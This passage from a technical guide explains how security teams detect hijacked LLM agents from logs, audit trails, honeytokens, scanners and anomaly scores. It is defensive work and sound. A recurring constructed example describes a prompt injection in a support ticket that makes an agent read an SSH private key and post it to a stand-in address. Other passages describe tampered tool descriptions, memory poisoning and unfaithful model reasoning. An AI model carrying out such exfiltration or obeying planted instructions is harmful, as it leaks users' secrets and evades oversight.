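| Operating system | Files, processes, connections and decrypted model traffic | Actions on other companies' servers | 2.9% slowdown on average in AgentSight's three tests; administrator rights |

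### How much kernel records help

Kernel records are bulky and awkward to collect. In *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security*, King, Zhang and colleagues (2026) recorded 4,047 sessions to measure how much these records help a detector. In each session, an agent running Claude Haiku 4.5 worked in a fresh container, an isolated environment on a shared machine. For each session, the researchers saved the transcript, the list of tools the agent received and about 3,500 kernel events. They attacked the agent through tampered MCP servers, files, web pages, memory, retrieved documents and the user's own prompt. They counted a session as malicious only if the records showed that the attack had taken effect.

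They then gave ten detectors the transcript and tool list, the kernel events, or both. They measured performance by AUROC, the probability that a detector gives a randomly chosen attack a higher score than a randomly chosen harmless session. Random guessing scores 0.5 and a perfect detector scores 1.

When the test attacks resembled the training attacks, all ten detectors did best with both kernel events and the transcript. In a harder test, with families of attack absent from training, seven of the ten still did best with both. One of them, the standard machine-learning method XGBoost, rose from 0.750 with kernel events alone to 0.850 with both. But the highest score in the harder test, 0.922, came from a small Llama model that the researchers had fine-tuned on kernel events alone, so adding the transcript does not always help.

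The averages conceal large differences between attacks. These are mean scores across the ten detectors in the easier test:

| Attack | Transcript and tool list | Kernel events | Both |
|---|---|---|---|
| Credentials secretly copied to a log file | 0.586 | 0.976 | 0.970 |
| Injection through a retrieved reference | 0.906 | 0.703 | 0.927 |
| Manipulation of the agent's preferences | 0.687 | 0.701 | 0.834 |

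In the secret copying, the transcript records neither the reading of the credentials nor the writing of the copy, so a detector that reads only the transcript does little better than guessing. Kernel events therefore help detect some of the attacks in which a hostile tool does not try to manipulate the model, but only if the tool runs on the company's own machine. The retrieved reference changes only text and leaves no distinctive kernel events.

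Most companies could not copy this set-up directly. King and colleagues ran each session in its own container so they could tell which events belonged to it. They left out agents inside code editors and desktop applications, which are the agents Uber monitors.

The researchers also tested the trained detectors on 592 sessions from a different model in a different harness. Three of the four kinds of detector still worked acceptably, but TabPFN, a model for tabular data, fell to 0.662. It had relied on a count of temporary files, which Claude's harness creates in every session but the other harness often does not.

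### Agents that nobody registered

Every collection method covers only the machines and programs where it has been set up. An employee can install an agent without telling anyone, or write one in a few dozen lines of script, and no log will include its sessions. Canale and Soulis (2026), in *Detecting Shadow AI*, cite vendor data from nearly 10,000 developer environments, in which 50.8% of developers had installed at least one MCP server.

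Searching for agents by their behavior alone produces too many false alarms, because an ordinary program installing a software package also keeps a connection to a remote service and runs commands. Canale and Soulis therefore built Agent Detector, a Windows program that scans a computer every hour for processes connected to known LLM services. It combines these connections with other clues, such as whether the process started a command shell and which MCP servers appear in the user's settings files.

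Agent Detector was tested on one workstation, in five rounds, with 12 synthetic agents and a set of look-alike programs that contacted services unrelated to AI. It found every agent in most rounds and flagged none of the look-alikes, whereas two rules based only on behaviour flagged all the look-alikes.

An Agent Detector scan takes about 154 milliseconds, but it can easily miss an agent because of its timing. Many LLM services share network addresses with unrelated sites, and the tool can distinguish them only while Windows still stores the domain name that was looked up, which it does for one to five minutes. About one scan in three caught an agent that connected intermittently. The tool also missed very short-lived agents, agents that reached a model through an undeclared relay, and agents inside WSL 2, a Linux environment within Windows.

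Agent Detector is designed not to inspect what an agent reads or writes. A hit shows that an agent exists, but the team still has to start logging it. Evidence of what the agent did before logging began is probably lost, unless the agent program kept its own history.

### Actions on a provider's servers

When an agent runs on a provider's servers, the customer usually can't add a recorder and has to rely on the provider's log. *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You*, published by the security company Pistachio, is a first-hand account of a logging failure that its employee Zack Korman found in July 2025. Microsoft 365 Copilot normally leaves an audit record when it opens a file for an employee. But if the employee asked Copilot to summarize a file without linking to it, Copilot gave the summary and the audit log did not show that it had opened the file.

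Korman found the flaw by accident when he noticed unreliable records while testing one of his company's own products, so other customers had probably lost records by accident too. He later learned that Michael Bargury of Zenity had reported the same problem a year earlier. Microsoft rated the flaw "important" and finished fixing it in August. Korman says Microsoft told him it had no plans to inform customers. Office 365 IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) and heise online's *AI assistant* also covered the gap and the fix.

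Investigators therefore can't treat a missing entry in Copilot records from before 18 August 2025 as proof that Copilot didn't access a file. Korman was worried about dishonest employees, but an attacker could also have planted text instructing Copilot to omit the link. The EchoLeak email contained a similar instruction never to mention the email.

The provider's records of an agent's settings can also have gaps. Datadog Security Labs' *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (2026) describes tests of Microsoft's tool for building custom agents. In August 2025, someone with editing rights could remove an agent's login requirement, turn off its conversation logging and publish the new version without leaving an audit record. Anyone who could reach the agent could then question it anonymously, also without a record. Microsoft fixed the audit logging by October, but later tests found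 that changes to the login and logging settings were again recorded only some of the time. The problem was still present in March 2026, and Microsoft said it could not reproduce it.

Datadog sells log monitoring and benefits from such findings, but any customer can repeat its test. Datadog's researchers created an agent, performed several actions that Microsoft's documentation listed as logged, waited 24 hours and searched for the records. A team should run a check like this before it relies on a provider's log, and repeat it from time to time, since a logging gap can return after it has been fixed.

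A complete audit log may still lack the text of prompts and replies. Splunk's *Getting Started With Copilot Log Analysis for Security in Microsoft 365* explains that Microsoft keeps this text out of its main audit log for privacy and security reasons, so an analyst has to fetch it through Purview eDiscovery, a separate tool for legal and compliance searches.

### Reasoning as evidence

Many models write out their reasoning before they act, and both AgentTrace and Uber's sensor collect it. In OPS-214, the model might write between records 3 and 4 that the ticket contains a request for a key file, which would be strong evidence of a hijacked session. But an innocent explanation in the same place would be weak evidence that nothing was wrong, because the model would have written it just after reading the attacker's text, which can include a cover story. In the AgentSight test, the hidden instruction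 presented the theft as a necessary step in building the project.

Models can also leave out what influenced them without being told to. Researchers at Anthropic tested this in *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think* (2025) by adding hints to multiple-choice questions and checking whether the model mentioned the hint when it had changed the model's answer. Claude 3.7 Sonnet mentioned the hint in 25% of these cases and DeepSeek R1 in 39%. Newer models have replaced both, and answering a quiz is very different from carrying out a theft, but an analyst can't assume that a model's written reasoning is complete.

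Some tools infer an agent's reasoning when the log doesn't contain it. Watson, described by Wang and colleagues, reconstructs a plausible line of reasoning from the agent's inputs and outputs. The reconstruction may help an analyst form a theory, but it should be labeled as such in the log because the agent never wrote it.

### Keeping the log out of the attacker's reach

An attacker who steers an agent with file access can tell it to edit its own history. Uber's sensor reads files stored on the agent's computer, so an attacker has up to an hour to change them. It is safer to send each record immediately to a separate machine, through an account that can add records but not change or delete them. *aiAuthZ* (2026) describes such a system, in which the agent's machine holds none of the keys.

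Records can also disappear without an attacker. *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* reports a test in which several programs wrote to the same log at once. With two programs, 9.66% of the records were lost without an error message, and with eight, 31.32% were. A program that reads the log may silently skip damaged lines. Numbering the records at their source makes these losses detectable.

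A hash chain reveals later changes. A hash function such as SHA-256 turns any text into a short fingerprint, and even a tiny change to the text produces a different fingerprint. In the scheme described in *Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models* (2026), the software calculates each record's fingerprint from the record joined to the previous fingerprint:

h(n) = SHA-256(record n + h(n−1))

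The chain starts from the fixed word GENESIS. The example below treats records 4 to 6 of OPS-214 as the whole log. The fingerprints are invented and much shorter than real ones, which have 64 characters.

| Record | Content | Previous fingerprint | Own fingerprint |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4 | `read_file`, SSH key | GENESIS | a91c |
| 5 | Private key (masked) | a91c | 5e07 |
| 6 | `http_post`, 203.0.113.20 | 5e07 | c3f8 |

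Suppose an attacker changes the path in record 4 to a harmless notes file. A program that recalculates the chain gets 17be for that record instead of a91c and reports a mismatch. If the attacker also replaces a91c with 17be, the mismatch moves to record 5, whose fingerprint depends on a91c. To hide the change, the attacker has to recalculate every later fingerprint, which is easy for anyone who can write to the whole log because the formula contains no secret.

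Deleting record 6 is even easier, because records 4 and 5 still form a valid chain. *BioFirewall* (2026) points out that removing records from the end of a valid chain always leaves a valid chain. The remedy is to keep the latest fingerprint and the number of records somewhere the attacker can't reach. If "c3f8, three records" is stored elsewhere, both the rewritten log and the shortened one fail the check. Including a secret key in the fingerprint calculation also stops an attacker who can write to the log but doesn't have the key.

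The outside copy protects only the records that existed when it was made. The OPS-214 session lasted 15 seconds, so with hourly copies an attacker could probably erase all its records before the next copy. *AuthGuard-R* (2026), a design for robots controlled by language models, allows a new copy after every privileged action in high-risk settings. A chain also can't reveal an event that was never logged, so Korman's missing Copilot records would have left no break in one. *Agent Flight Recorder* (2026), which describes a tamper-evident recorder for agents, explicitly excludes completeness from its goals.

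### Secrets, personal data and how long to keep them

Masking keeps the SSH key out of record 5, but the prompts and tickets in a log also contain personal data about employees and customers. Uber's system removes the secrets that automated scanning can find in stored records, encrypts data in transit, and limits access to security staff.

Masking secrets can destroy useful evidence, but the OPS-214 log still shows that the agent sent exactly what it had read, because the logging software marked the two masked values as identical. Software can do this by storing a fingerprint of each secret, calculated with a key kept outside the log. If the fingerprint were calculated without a key, someone who stole the log could guess short passwords and check each guess against it.

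Uber keeps its records for 13 months. Keeping records this long helps analysts investigate memory poisoning, where an attacker may plant a false note in an agent's memory weeks before the theft. If a company deletes its records after 30 days, an analyst investigating a theft in late April can't find the March session in which the agent saved the note.

Deleting old records would normally break a hash chain. *aiAuthZ* avoids this by calculating the chain from hashes of the content and storing the encrypted content in a separate field. When the retention period ends, the system clears that field and keeps the rest of the record. An auditor can still confirm that the agent made a particular call and whether the system allowed it, but nobody can recover the personal data that was in the cleared field.

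The EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime (Article 12). Companies that provide or use these systems must keep the logs under their control for at least six months (Articles 19 and 26). An agent that screens job applicants would normally count as high-risk, but one that only summarizes support tickets would not.

These duties were due to begin in August 2026. The National Law Review's *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026) reports that an amending law has moved the high-risk rules to 2 December 2027 for listed uses such as recruitment, and to 2 August 2028 for AI in products that already have their own safety rules. For most systems, Article 12 states what the logs are for but doesn't list the fields they must contain, so a company could comply with it and still have no record of which text came from a stranger.

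## Writing rules for known attacks

A detection rule is a condition that a program checks against the log, raising an alert whenever the condition holds. The simplest rules need only the text of one record. Others also need a list of what the agent is allowed to do, the order of events in a session, the approved version of each tool description, or a planted fake credential.

### Matching phrases and addresses

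A phrase rule searches for words that attackers have used before. Soto's *Using Splunk to Develop Local LLM MCP Mitre Atlas Detections* gives working examples for Splunk, a product for storing and searching logs. Its prompt-injection rule counts messages that contain a word such as "ignore", "bypass" or "system", a phrase that gives the model a role to play, or any bracket or brace. The rule totals the counts over ten-minute windows and raises an alert if any total is above zero.

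This rule would probably flag almost every window on a working agent, because "system" is a common word in support tickets and tool calls usually take the form of JSON, a data format full of braces. The rule also pools the messages of everyone active in a window and lists all their addresses, so one suspicious message implicates every user who was online. Soto built the rules from attacks in his own lab and gives no false-positive rate. Ollama, the program that ran his model, usually leaves prompts out of its log, so to get text to search he installed a particular version, turned on debug logging and wrote scripts to convert the output into structured records.

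Phrase rules work better on text that the attacker can't reword. *From Attack Simulation to SIEM Rule* (2026) describes a program that turns the results of simulated attacks into rules for a SIEM, the platform where a security team collects and searches its logs. One of these rules detects attackers who ask an agent which tools it has. Attackers can phrase the question in many ways, but the answer tends to contain the same fragments of tool definitions, so the rule searches the agent's replies for those fragments. The program attaches a warning that teams should exclude documentation chatbots, which describe their tools legitimately.

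The planted paragraph in OPS-214 needs no stock phrase that a rule could match, and its author could quickly reword it. A rule for the address 203.0.113.20 would work only after someone had reported it, and the attacker could then rent another address. The rule is still worth running over old logs because it may find other sessions that sent data to the same address.

### Lists of permitted tools and destinations

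A list of permitted actions can catch attacks that nobody has seen before. The team lists the tools the agent may use and the addresses it may contact, and the rule raises an alert for anything else. If the only addresses on the support agent's list are the company's own servers, record 6 triggers an alert however the attacker worded the ticket. Record 4 does not trigger an alert, because the agent is allowed to use `read_file`. To catch it, the team would also have to list the permitted folders.

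Each agent needs its own list of permitted addresses. A deployment agent contacts servers that a support agent never should, and a shared list would let an attacker who hijacked either agent reach all of them. Even a narrow list fails if a permitted address forwards data elsewhere, as the Microsoft Teams address did in EchoLeak.

### A rule over several records

Each step of OPS-214 could be innocent by itself, but the sequence is suspicious. *Parasites in the Toolchain* (2025) divides one class of attack on MCP systems into three stages, in which outside content enters, a tool collects private data, and a tool sends the data out. A rule can follow the same stages:

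```
for each session:
    outside = first tool result with text from outside the company
    secret  = first tool result after outside that contains a secret
    send    = first tool call after secret that sends data
              to an address missing from the permitted list
    if outside, secret and send all exist:
        raise an alert that names the three records
```

For the rule to work, the log has to show where each tool result came from, and the masking software has to label secrets as secrets. Someone also has to list the tools that can send data. *Parasites in the Toolchain* describes a program that sorts MCP tools by their descriptions and then tests whether they can do what the descriptions suggest, which is a sensible way to build that list.

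On OPS-214, the rule works through the log as follows:

| Record | Event | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| 1–2 | Request; call to `get_ticket` | None |
| 3 | Ticket emailed from outside | `outside` = 3 |
| 4 | Call to `read_file` | None, because the call has not returned anything yet |
| 5 | Private key (masked) | `secret` = 5 |
| 6 | `http_post` to 203.0.113.20 | The address is unlisted, so `send` = 6 and the rule raises an alert |

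Now take a harmless session, also constructed, in which an employee asks an agent to install a program on a new server:

| Record | Event | Content |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | User request | Deploy the export service to our new test server, 198.51.100.7. Follow the hosting company's online guide. |
| 2 | Tool call | `fetch_page`, with the address of the guide |
| 3 | Tool result | Setup guide from the hosting company's website |
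| 4 | Tool call | `read_file(path="deploy/token")` |
| 5 | Tool result | Deployment token (masked) |
| 6 | Tool call | `http_post(address="198.51.100.7", body=…)`; body contains the program and the token |
| 7 | Tool result | Status 200, accepted |

The rule raises an alert here too, naming records 3, 5 and 6. The guide came from outside, the token is a secret, and nobody has added the new server to the list. Adding it would silence this alert, but the next new server would cause another. A more lasting change is to add a condition to the last test:

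```
    if outside, secret and send all exist
       and the user's request does not contain the address in send:
        raise an alert that names the three records
```

The employee typed 198.51.100.7 in the request, so the deployment no longer triggers an alert. The request in OPS-214 contains no address, so that alert remains.

The new condition can miss attacks because it relies on the user's request being trustworthy. An attacker with a stolen login can type his own address into the request, and an employee might paste in the text of a malicious email that includes the attacker's address. The condition also fails if the user names a public file-sharing site on which the attacker has an account. A team worried about stolen logins could lower the priority of these alerts instead of dropping them.

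Requiring that the agent sent exactly what it had read would not have helped, because the deployment also sends the token it read, and an attacker could evade the test by having the agent encode the key first.

Both versions of the rule miss an attack that deletes files, since it involves no secret and no outside address. They would catch the variant of OPS-214 in which the instruction is in the tool description and the ticket is clean, but only because the ticket also came from outside. The alert would list record 3 as the source, so the analyst would start by investigating the clean ticket.

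### Changes in a tool since its approval

To detect an altered tool, a rule needs a fingerprint of the tool's name, description, arguments and server address, taken before the session, when somebody approved the tool. A program recalculates the fingerprint at each connection and raises an alert if it has changed.

MCP clients typically don't do this themselves. *ETDI* (2025), a proposal for securing tool definitions, explains that a client may never fetch the full definition again after the user first approves the tool. If the name and version stay the same, the client may not ask the user for approval again. In its example, a tool called "Daily Wallpaper v1.0" keeps that name but starts searching the user's documents for financial keywords and uploading what it finds.

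The program should compare each description with the approved copy rather than the previous day's. Shen and colleagues warn of servers that change in small steps, none of which looks alarming alone. The rule's main drawback is that somebody must spend time reading legitimate updates.

The comparison can't detect an attacker who changes only the tool's code or a library that the code uses. If the wallpaper tool kept its old description, its fingerprint would still match. King and colleagues made 82 tampered versions of MCP servers for their study of kernel records, and 52 of them offered exactly the same tool list as the original, so the comparison could have flagged at most 30.

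### Planted credentials

A planted credential, often called a honeytoken or canary, is a fake password or key that no legitimate task requires, so anyone who uses it is probably an intruder. Security teams used them long before LLM agents existed. *PHANTOM* (2026) credits Spitzner with formalising the idea, which also covers fake user accounts, files and database records.

A company could put a fake key at `~/.ssh/id_ed25519` and keep the real one elsewhere. The agent in OPS-214 would then send the fake, and a server would raise an alarm when the attacker tried it at 09:40. Agent logs miss that login because they end before it happens. Encoding the key on its way out wouldn't prevent the alarm, because the attacker has to decode the key to use it.

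Searching an agent's output for the fake key gives an earlier warning but is less reliable. Chauhan and Revankar (2026), in *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, tested ways to detect a model leaking credentials from its context. On a small Qwen model, a plain search for the credential's text reached an AUROC of 0.73, with an 8% false-positive rate. Encoding or paraphrasing the credential is a known way to evade such searches. Their study also left out tool-call arguments, where the key appears in OPS-214.

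They give a simple formula for the chance of detection when an attacker takes one credential at random and can't tell real from fake:

P(detection) = k / (m + k) × (1 − β)

Here m is the number of real credentials, k is the number of fakes, and β is the share of leaked fakes that the detector misses. With one real key, three fakes and a detector that misses 10%, the chance of detection is 3/4 × 0.9, or about 68%. An attacker who knows where real keys are usually stored won't choose at random. If the ticket names one path, the chance depends on whether the key there is real or fake. An attacker who asks for every key is certain to take a fake.

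*Optional Traps* (Ghifiardi, 2026) describes experiments with small LLM agents as the attackers, in which the placement of traps mattered. The target was a mock records service with a debug page that leaked a real key. In the first experiment, Ghifiardi put a fake key in a backup file and added a fake internal service. The agent ignored both, took the real key from the debug page and exported the records in six requests. The experiment had one session for each of two set-ups, so it is only an example of what can happen.

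He then removed the leak and ran 20 sessions in each of three conditions with another model:

| Debug page | Records exported | Attacker detected and blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Leaks the real key | 20 of 20 | 0 of 20 |
| Removed | 0 of 20 | 0 of 20 |
| Offers a fake key | 0 of 20 | 19 of 20 |

Fixing the leak accounted for all the measurable prevention, and the fake key added detection. In the one session without an alarm, the agent read the page but tried a different credential, which was invalid. Ghifiardi had told the agents which pages to look at, so the result is weak evidence of whether an attacker would find the bait unaided.

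He also found that agents make one kind of false alarm more likely. In a later trial, a legitimate agent had the correct key in its instructions, but it opened the debug page, used the fake key instead and lost its access. People rarely swap a working password for one they happen to find. Ghifiardi therefore recommends treating the use of a fake credential as strong but inconclusive evidence of an attack, and responding with a measure that is easy to reverse, such as the 15-minute block in his experiments.

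### Ready-made scanners for tools

King and colleagues tested a free Cisco scanner that checks the tool descriptions an MCP server offers. They ran it offline with its YARA rules, which are text patterns in a format that malware analysts use. Across 1,871 sessions with MCP servers, the scanner flagged 116 of 731 attacks (15.9% recall) and 16.3% of the other sessions, so it was no more likely to flag an attacked session than any other.

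The false-positive rate somewhat overstates the scanner's errors. The "other" sessions include some in which the server had been tampered with but the attack had no effect, and flagging a malicious description there was arguably correct. The low recall is harder to justify. One rule requires exact phrases such as "sidenote required", but the planted descriptions made similar demands in other words. No description scanner, however, could have detected the 52 tampered servers whose tool lists had not changed.

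Scanning the code should help with those. Hu, Jia and colleagues (2026), in *MalTool*, used LLMs to write malicious functions of 13 kinds, from stealing files to wasting processor time, and hid them in 5,727 real tools. They ran six scanners on the results, and on 1,147 code repositories of harmless tools. These are averages calculated from their rates for each kind of attack and each category of tool:

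| Scanner | Malicious tools flagged | Harmless repositories flagged |
|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 0.3% | 0% |
| Bandit | 86% | 63% |
| Semgrep | 43% | 17% |
| Tencent A.I.G | 37% | 38% |
| AntGroup MCPScan | 37% | 36% |
| Cisco MCP Scanner | 37% | 0.6% |
| Any of the six | 92% | 66% |

VirusTotal combines many antivirus products, which mostly recognise known malware, but the malicious tools tested here were new. Bandit searches for insecure coding patterns, which many harmless programs also contain. Its 86% overstates how well it detects malicious code, because that code was inside real tools that Bandit might have flagged anyway. The Tencent and AntGroup scanners did no better than guessing.

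The Cisco scanner gave the most useful results. In this test it used an LLM to analyse the code, unlike the offline version that King and colleagues tested, and it almost never flagged a harmless repository. It caught 86% of the tools that sent the user's prompts to an outside server, but none of those that planted false records in a database. A team could therefore act on its alerts, but the lack of an alert doesn't show that a repository is safe.

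Some of the "harmless" tools may have been malicious, but two of the researchers checked 200 tools from this group that at least one scanner had flagged and found no explicit malicious behaviour.

### Rule engines that watch the computer

Falco, a free rule engine for Linux, checks kernel events against about 100 default rules. King and colleagues applied the rules that their recordings could support, and every session triggered at least one. Falco therefore had 100% recall and a 100% false-positive rate, the opposite failure from the Cisco scanner's. Counting how many rules each session triggered barely helped separate attacks from benign sessions, with an AUROC of about 0.57.

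The default rules are written for ordinary servers, where programs do not normally open a command shell, read system account files or create hidden files. Claude Code, the agent program in this study, does all three in routine work. The rule for unexpected shells fired in 99.3% of harmless sessions and 99.2% of attacks. A rule for connections to unusual ports was more informative, firing in 4.6% of harmless sessions and 13.4% of attacks. A team that switched off the three noisy rules and kept the port rule would have far fewer alerts but would still miss most attacks.

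Tuning is harder when an attack looks exactly like the agent's normal work. Chen, Denis and colleagues (2026), in *Self-State Attacks on Self-Hosted AI Agents*, studied attacks on the files in which an agent keeps its own memory, instructions and settings. They tested detectors on 55 attacks and 60 harmless sessions:

| Detector | What it checks | Attacks flagged | Harmless sessions flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
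| AIDE | Whether protected files changed | 52 of 55 | 32 of 60 |
| Falco | Rules about system events | 43 of 55 | 21 of 60 |
| STIDE | System-call sequences absent from normal sessions | 55 of 55 | 58 of 60 |

Among the harmless sessions, AIDE flagged exactly the 32 in which the agent changed its own files. It detected changes but couldn't distinguish malicious ones from legitimate ones. Methods that examined the size and timing of each write raised as few as 3 false alerts, but could assess only 23 of the 55 attacks. The best of these low-alert methods flagged 15 attacks.

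When a hijacked agent saves a false note, it writes to the same file, from the same account, and with the same operation as an agent saving a legitimate one, so a rule based only on those details can't distinguish them. Chen and colleagues suggest making approved updates look different, for instance by sending them through a separate trusted program. A simple rule could then raise an alert for any write that bypassed that program. They didn't test this, and it wouldn't help if the attacker got the trusted program to accept a false note.

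### Which rules are worth maintaining

Rules work best on things an attacker can't easily change. An attacker can reword a ticket in a minute, but still needs somewhere to receive the data and has to use a stolen key to benefit from it. Destination lists, planted credentials and the three-stage rule therefore deserve more effort than phrase lists. Rules also suit secrets with a fixed format, as Uber's check for leaked credentials showed. They are a poor choice for an injection that only distorts a summary, because no fixed pattern separates a bad summary from a good one.

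Writing rules takes time and skill, according to *RulePilot* (2025), which describes an LLM agent that drafts them from an analyst's instructions. The drafts still need testing on the company's own logs. A team should keep sessions like OPS-214 and the deployment as test cases and test the rule on both after every edit, since a change that removes a false alert can also stop the rule from detecting the attack. It should also repeat the tests after every update to the agent software. If an update renames a log field, a rule that reads the old name will match nothing and probably give no error.

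Adding generic rules to a learned detector may achieve little. In King and colleagues' comparison, the machine-learning method XGBoost missed 57 attacks on MCP servers. Cisco's offline scanner flagged 8 of them (14%), but it flagged sessions without a successful attack at a slightly higher rate. A company's own rules can do better because they use facts that a detector can't learn from past sessions, such as which key is fake or which tool description somebody approved. They also work from the first day, without example attacks to train on, and take little computing power. When the three-stage rule flags OPS-214, the alert lists records 3, 5 and 6, so an analyst can check it by reading three lines.

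## Scoring sessions by how far they depart from normal

For a rule to work, somebody has to decide in advance what an agent must not do. A statistical detector instead learns from past sessions and scores each new session by how far it departs from normal. The team sends sessions that score above a chosen threshold to an analyst. This method can catch attacks that nobody wrote a rule for, but it can also flag many unusual sessions that are harmless and miss some attacks that look ordinary.

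### Turning a trace into something a detector can score

Software first has to reduce each session to numbers or symbols, and the detector can't use anything left out at this stage. OPS-214 looks like this in four common forms:

| Form | OPS-214 | What it leaves out |
|---|---|---|
| Counts | One call each to `get_ticket`, `read_file` and `http_post` | The order of the calls and their contents |
| Order | `get_ticket`, `read_file`, `http_post`, reply | Which file the agent read and where it sent the data |
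| Arguments and text | The ticket's text, the key file's path, the address 203.0.113.20 | Often the order, because many detectors average over the calls |
| Graph | `read_file` linked to `http_post`, because the file's contents appear in the request | Links that the matching can't find, such as data the agent encoded first |

Text needs the most preparation. A sentence encoder (a small language model) converts each passage into an embedding, a list of several hundred numbers. Passages with similar meanings get similar embeddings, so a detector can learn that the path of an SSH key is unlike the paths a support agent normally opens.

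Building a graph requires a rule for which calls to link. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (Zavrak, 2026) links each call to the next one, and also links two calls when the beginning of one result reappears in the other's arguments. If the masking software preserves the match, `read_file` and `http_post` get this second kind of link. `get_ticket` and `read_file` do not, because the rule covers only the beginning of the ticket and the key file's path is in the ticket's last paragraph. Investigators can use similar graphs to trace an alert back to its source.

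### Learning from normal sessions or from labelled attacks

Some detectors train only on normal sessions and flag sessions that differ from them. *Real-Time Detection and Repair of LLM Agent Failures* (2026) describes monitors that learn from healthy runs without any examples of failure. This approach suits a company that has thousands of ordinary sessions and no confirmed attack. However, agents often do harmless things for the first time, and these detectors can flag them. STIDE, for instance, flagged nearly all the harmless sessions in Chen and colleagues' test.

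A classifier trains on sessions labelled as attacks or harmless. If the harmless examples include unusual sessions, it can learn not to flag such sessions. However, most labelled attacks come from researchers' benchmarks, so a classifier may learn patterns specific to those benchmarks and miss attacks built differently.

### A transition score worked by hand

The simplest detector trained on normal sessions counts which step usually follows which. Suppose a support agent's past logs contain the following counts, all of them invented:

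| Step | Count | Share | Score, −ln(share) |
|---|---|---|---|
| `get_ticket` → reply | 900 of 1,000 | 0.9 | 0.1 |
| `get_ticket` → `read_file` | 5 of 1,000 | 0.005 | 5.3 |
| `read_file` → `http_post` | 2 of 400 | 0.005 | 5.3 |
| `get_ticket` → `get_export` | 60 of 1,000 | 0.06 | 2.8 |
| `get_export` → `send_email` | 76 of 80 | 0.95 | 0.05 |

The score of a step is the negative natural logarithm of its share, so rare steps score high and a step that always happens scores zero. Adding the scores is equivalent to multiplying the shares. The two hijacked steps in OPS-214 total 10.6, which corresponds to a chance of 0.005 × 0.005, or one in 40,000. An ordinary session, in which the agent reads the ticket and replies, scores 0.1. With a threshold of 8, the detector flags OPS-214 but not the ordinary session.

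Suppose an employee asks the agent to email a customer the latest export. The agent calls `get_ticket`, `get_export` and `send_email`, and the two steps between these calls give the session a total score of about 2.9. In a hijacked version of this session, a planted paragraph in the ticket gives the attacker's address as the customer's new one, and the agent sends the export there. The score is still about 2.9 because the agent calls the same tools in the same order. Lowering the threshold can't separate the two sessions, because their tool calls differ only in the email address and the detector doesn't use arguments.

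Adding up step scores also makes long sessions look suspicious, since a hundred ordinary steps at 0.1 each total about as much as the theft in OPS-214. Dividing by the number of steps fixes that but hides short hijacks, because a session with two hijacked steps and 98 ordinary ones averages only 0.2. *Real-Time Detection and Repair of LLM Agent Failures* uses CUSUM, an older statistical method that keeps a running total of how surprising recent steps were. Ordinary steps bring the total back down, so it builds up only when surprising steps come close together.

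### Learning a fixed workflow

The detector in *TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) learns an agent's whole workflow from normal sessions, rather than only pairs of steps. It needs only the order of the tool calls and their arguments and results, all of which a gateway can record.

One of the agents used to test TraceAegis directs patients to hospital departments. It calls one tool to get a list of valid symptom keywords and a second to get recommended departments, then fetches a checklist from each department. TraceAegis assigns each tool a level based on where it appears in past sessions. Orthopaedics sometimes comes before psychiatry and sometimes after, so TraceAegis puts both on the same level and ignores their order. It then splits each session into short units, such as keywords, then recommendation, then orthopaedics. It can therefore accept a new combination of departments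 if each unit appeared in past sessions.

A language model then uses the past examples to write a rule for each unit, such as sending patients with knee or arm pain to orthopaedics. When a new session arrives, TraceAegis first checks whether every unit is familiar. If so, a language model checks whether the session meets the rules' conditions.

Liu and colleagues tested this on the hospital agent and on one that handles purchase requests. For each agent they collected 1,300 normal sessions and 300 abnormal ones. Half of the abnormal sessions had an unfamiliar order of calls, and the other half had a familiar order with the wrong content, such as back pain leading to psychiatry. With DeepSeek-V3 as the language model, the detector caught the following:

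| Abnormal sessions | TraceAegis | DeepSeek-V3 alone |
|---|---|---|
| Hospital, unfamiliar order | 141 of 150 | 120 of 150 |
| Hospital, wrong content | 148 of 150 | 113 of 150 |
| Purchasing, unfamiliar order | 150 of 150 | 143 of 150 |
| Purchasing, wrong content | 130 of 150 | 84 of 150 |

Precision was 97% for the hospital agent and 93% for the purchasing agent, on tests where about half the sessions were abnormal. The content check depended heavily on the choice of language model. With the smaller Gemma 3 27B, TraceAegis caught only 64 of the 150 purchasing sessions with wrong content, though it still caught every session whose steps came in an unfamiliar order.

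Liu and colleagues also tried TraceAegis on a technology company's agent for finding software vulnerabilities, while an internal team attacked the agent. In one attack, a hidden payload in a configuration file made the agent write its report before running its checks. TraceAegis caught 132 of 140 such sessions (94%). The researchers give no false-positive rate for this trial.

All three agents follow a largely fixed workflow, which is the main reason to doubt that the results would carry over to other agents. A coding agent may read files, run tests and search the web in almost any order, so many of its harmless sessions would contain an unfamiliar unit.

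The content check is also lenient. According to the published prompt, two sets of conditions match if at least one pair of items is similar, and extra items don't matter. If a hijacked agent emailed an export to both the customer and the attacker, the customer's address might be enough for a match.

### Structure without words

Iyer (2026), in *Structural Representations for Cross-Attack Generalization in AI Agent Threat Detection*, claims that the shape of a session is often enough to reveal an attack. This would be useful because an attacker can reword a planted instruction endlessly. Iyer compared two ways of turning a session into symbols. The "structural" set has nine symbols for events such as a user message, a tool call, its arguments, its result and an error. The "conversational" set has 26, which mark suspicious phrases, refusals, types of tool and patterns in the arguments.

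Iyer generated 2,500 synthetic sessions, half of them attacks of five kinds. He trained a small sequence-reading neural network on four kinds of attack and tested it on the fifth, to stand in for an attack nobody has seen before. He reports the results as AUC (also called AUROC), the area under the curve of recall against the false-positive rate as the threshold moves. If the attack in OPS-214 scores 10.6 and four harmless sessions score 0.1, 2.9, 5 and 12, the attack outscores three of the four, so the AUC is 0.75.

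| Attack absent from training | Structural | Conversational | Both, combined |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool hijacking | 0.85 | 0.39 | 0.60 |
| Data theft | 0.85 | 0.46 | 0.62 |
| Uncategorised | 0.97 | 0.26 | 0.92 |
| Prompt injection | 0.81 | 0.69 | 0.83 |
| Social engineering | 0.67 | 0.78 | 0.89 |

An AUC of 0.39 is worse than guessing, because the detector tended to score harmless sessions higher than attacks. In the test on uncategorised attacks, it gave harmless sessions an average attack probability of 0.97, compared with 0.69 for attacks. At any ordinary threshold, it would have produced far too many false alerts for a team to handle.

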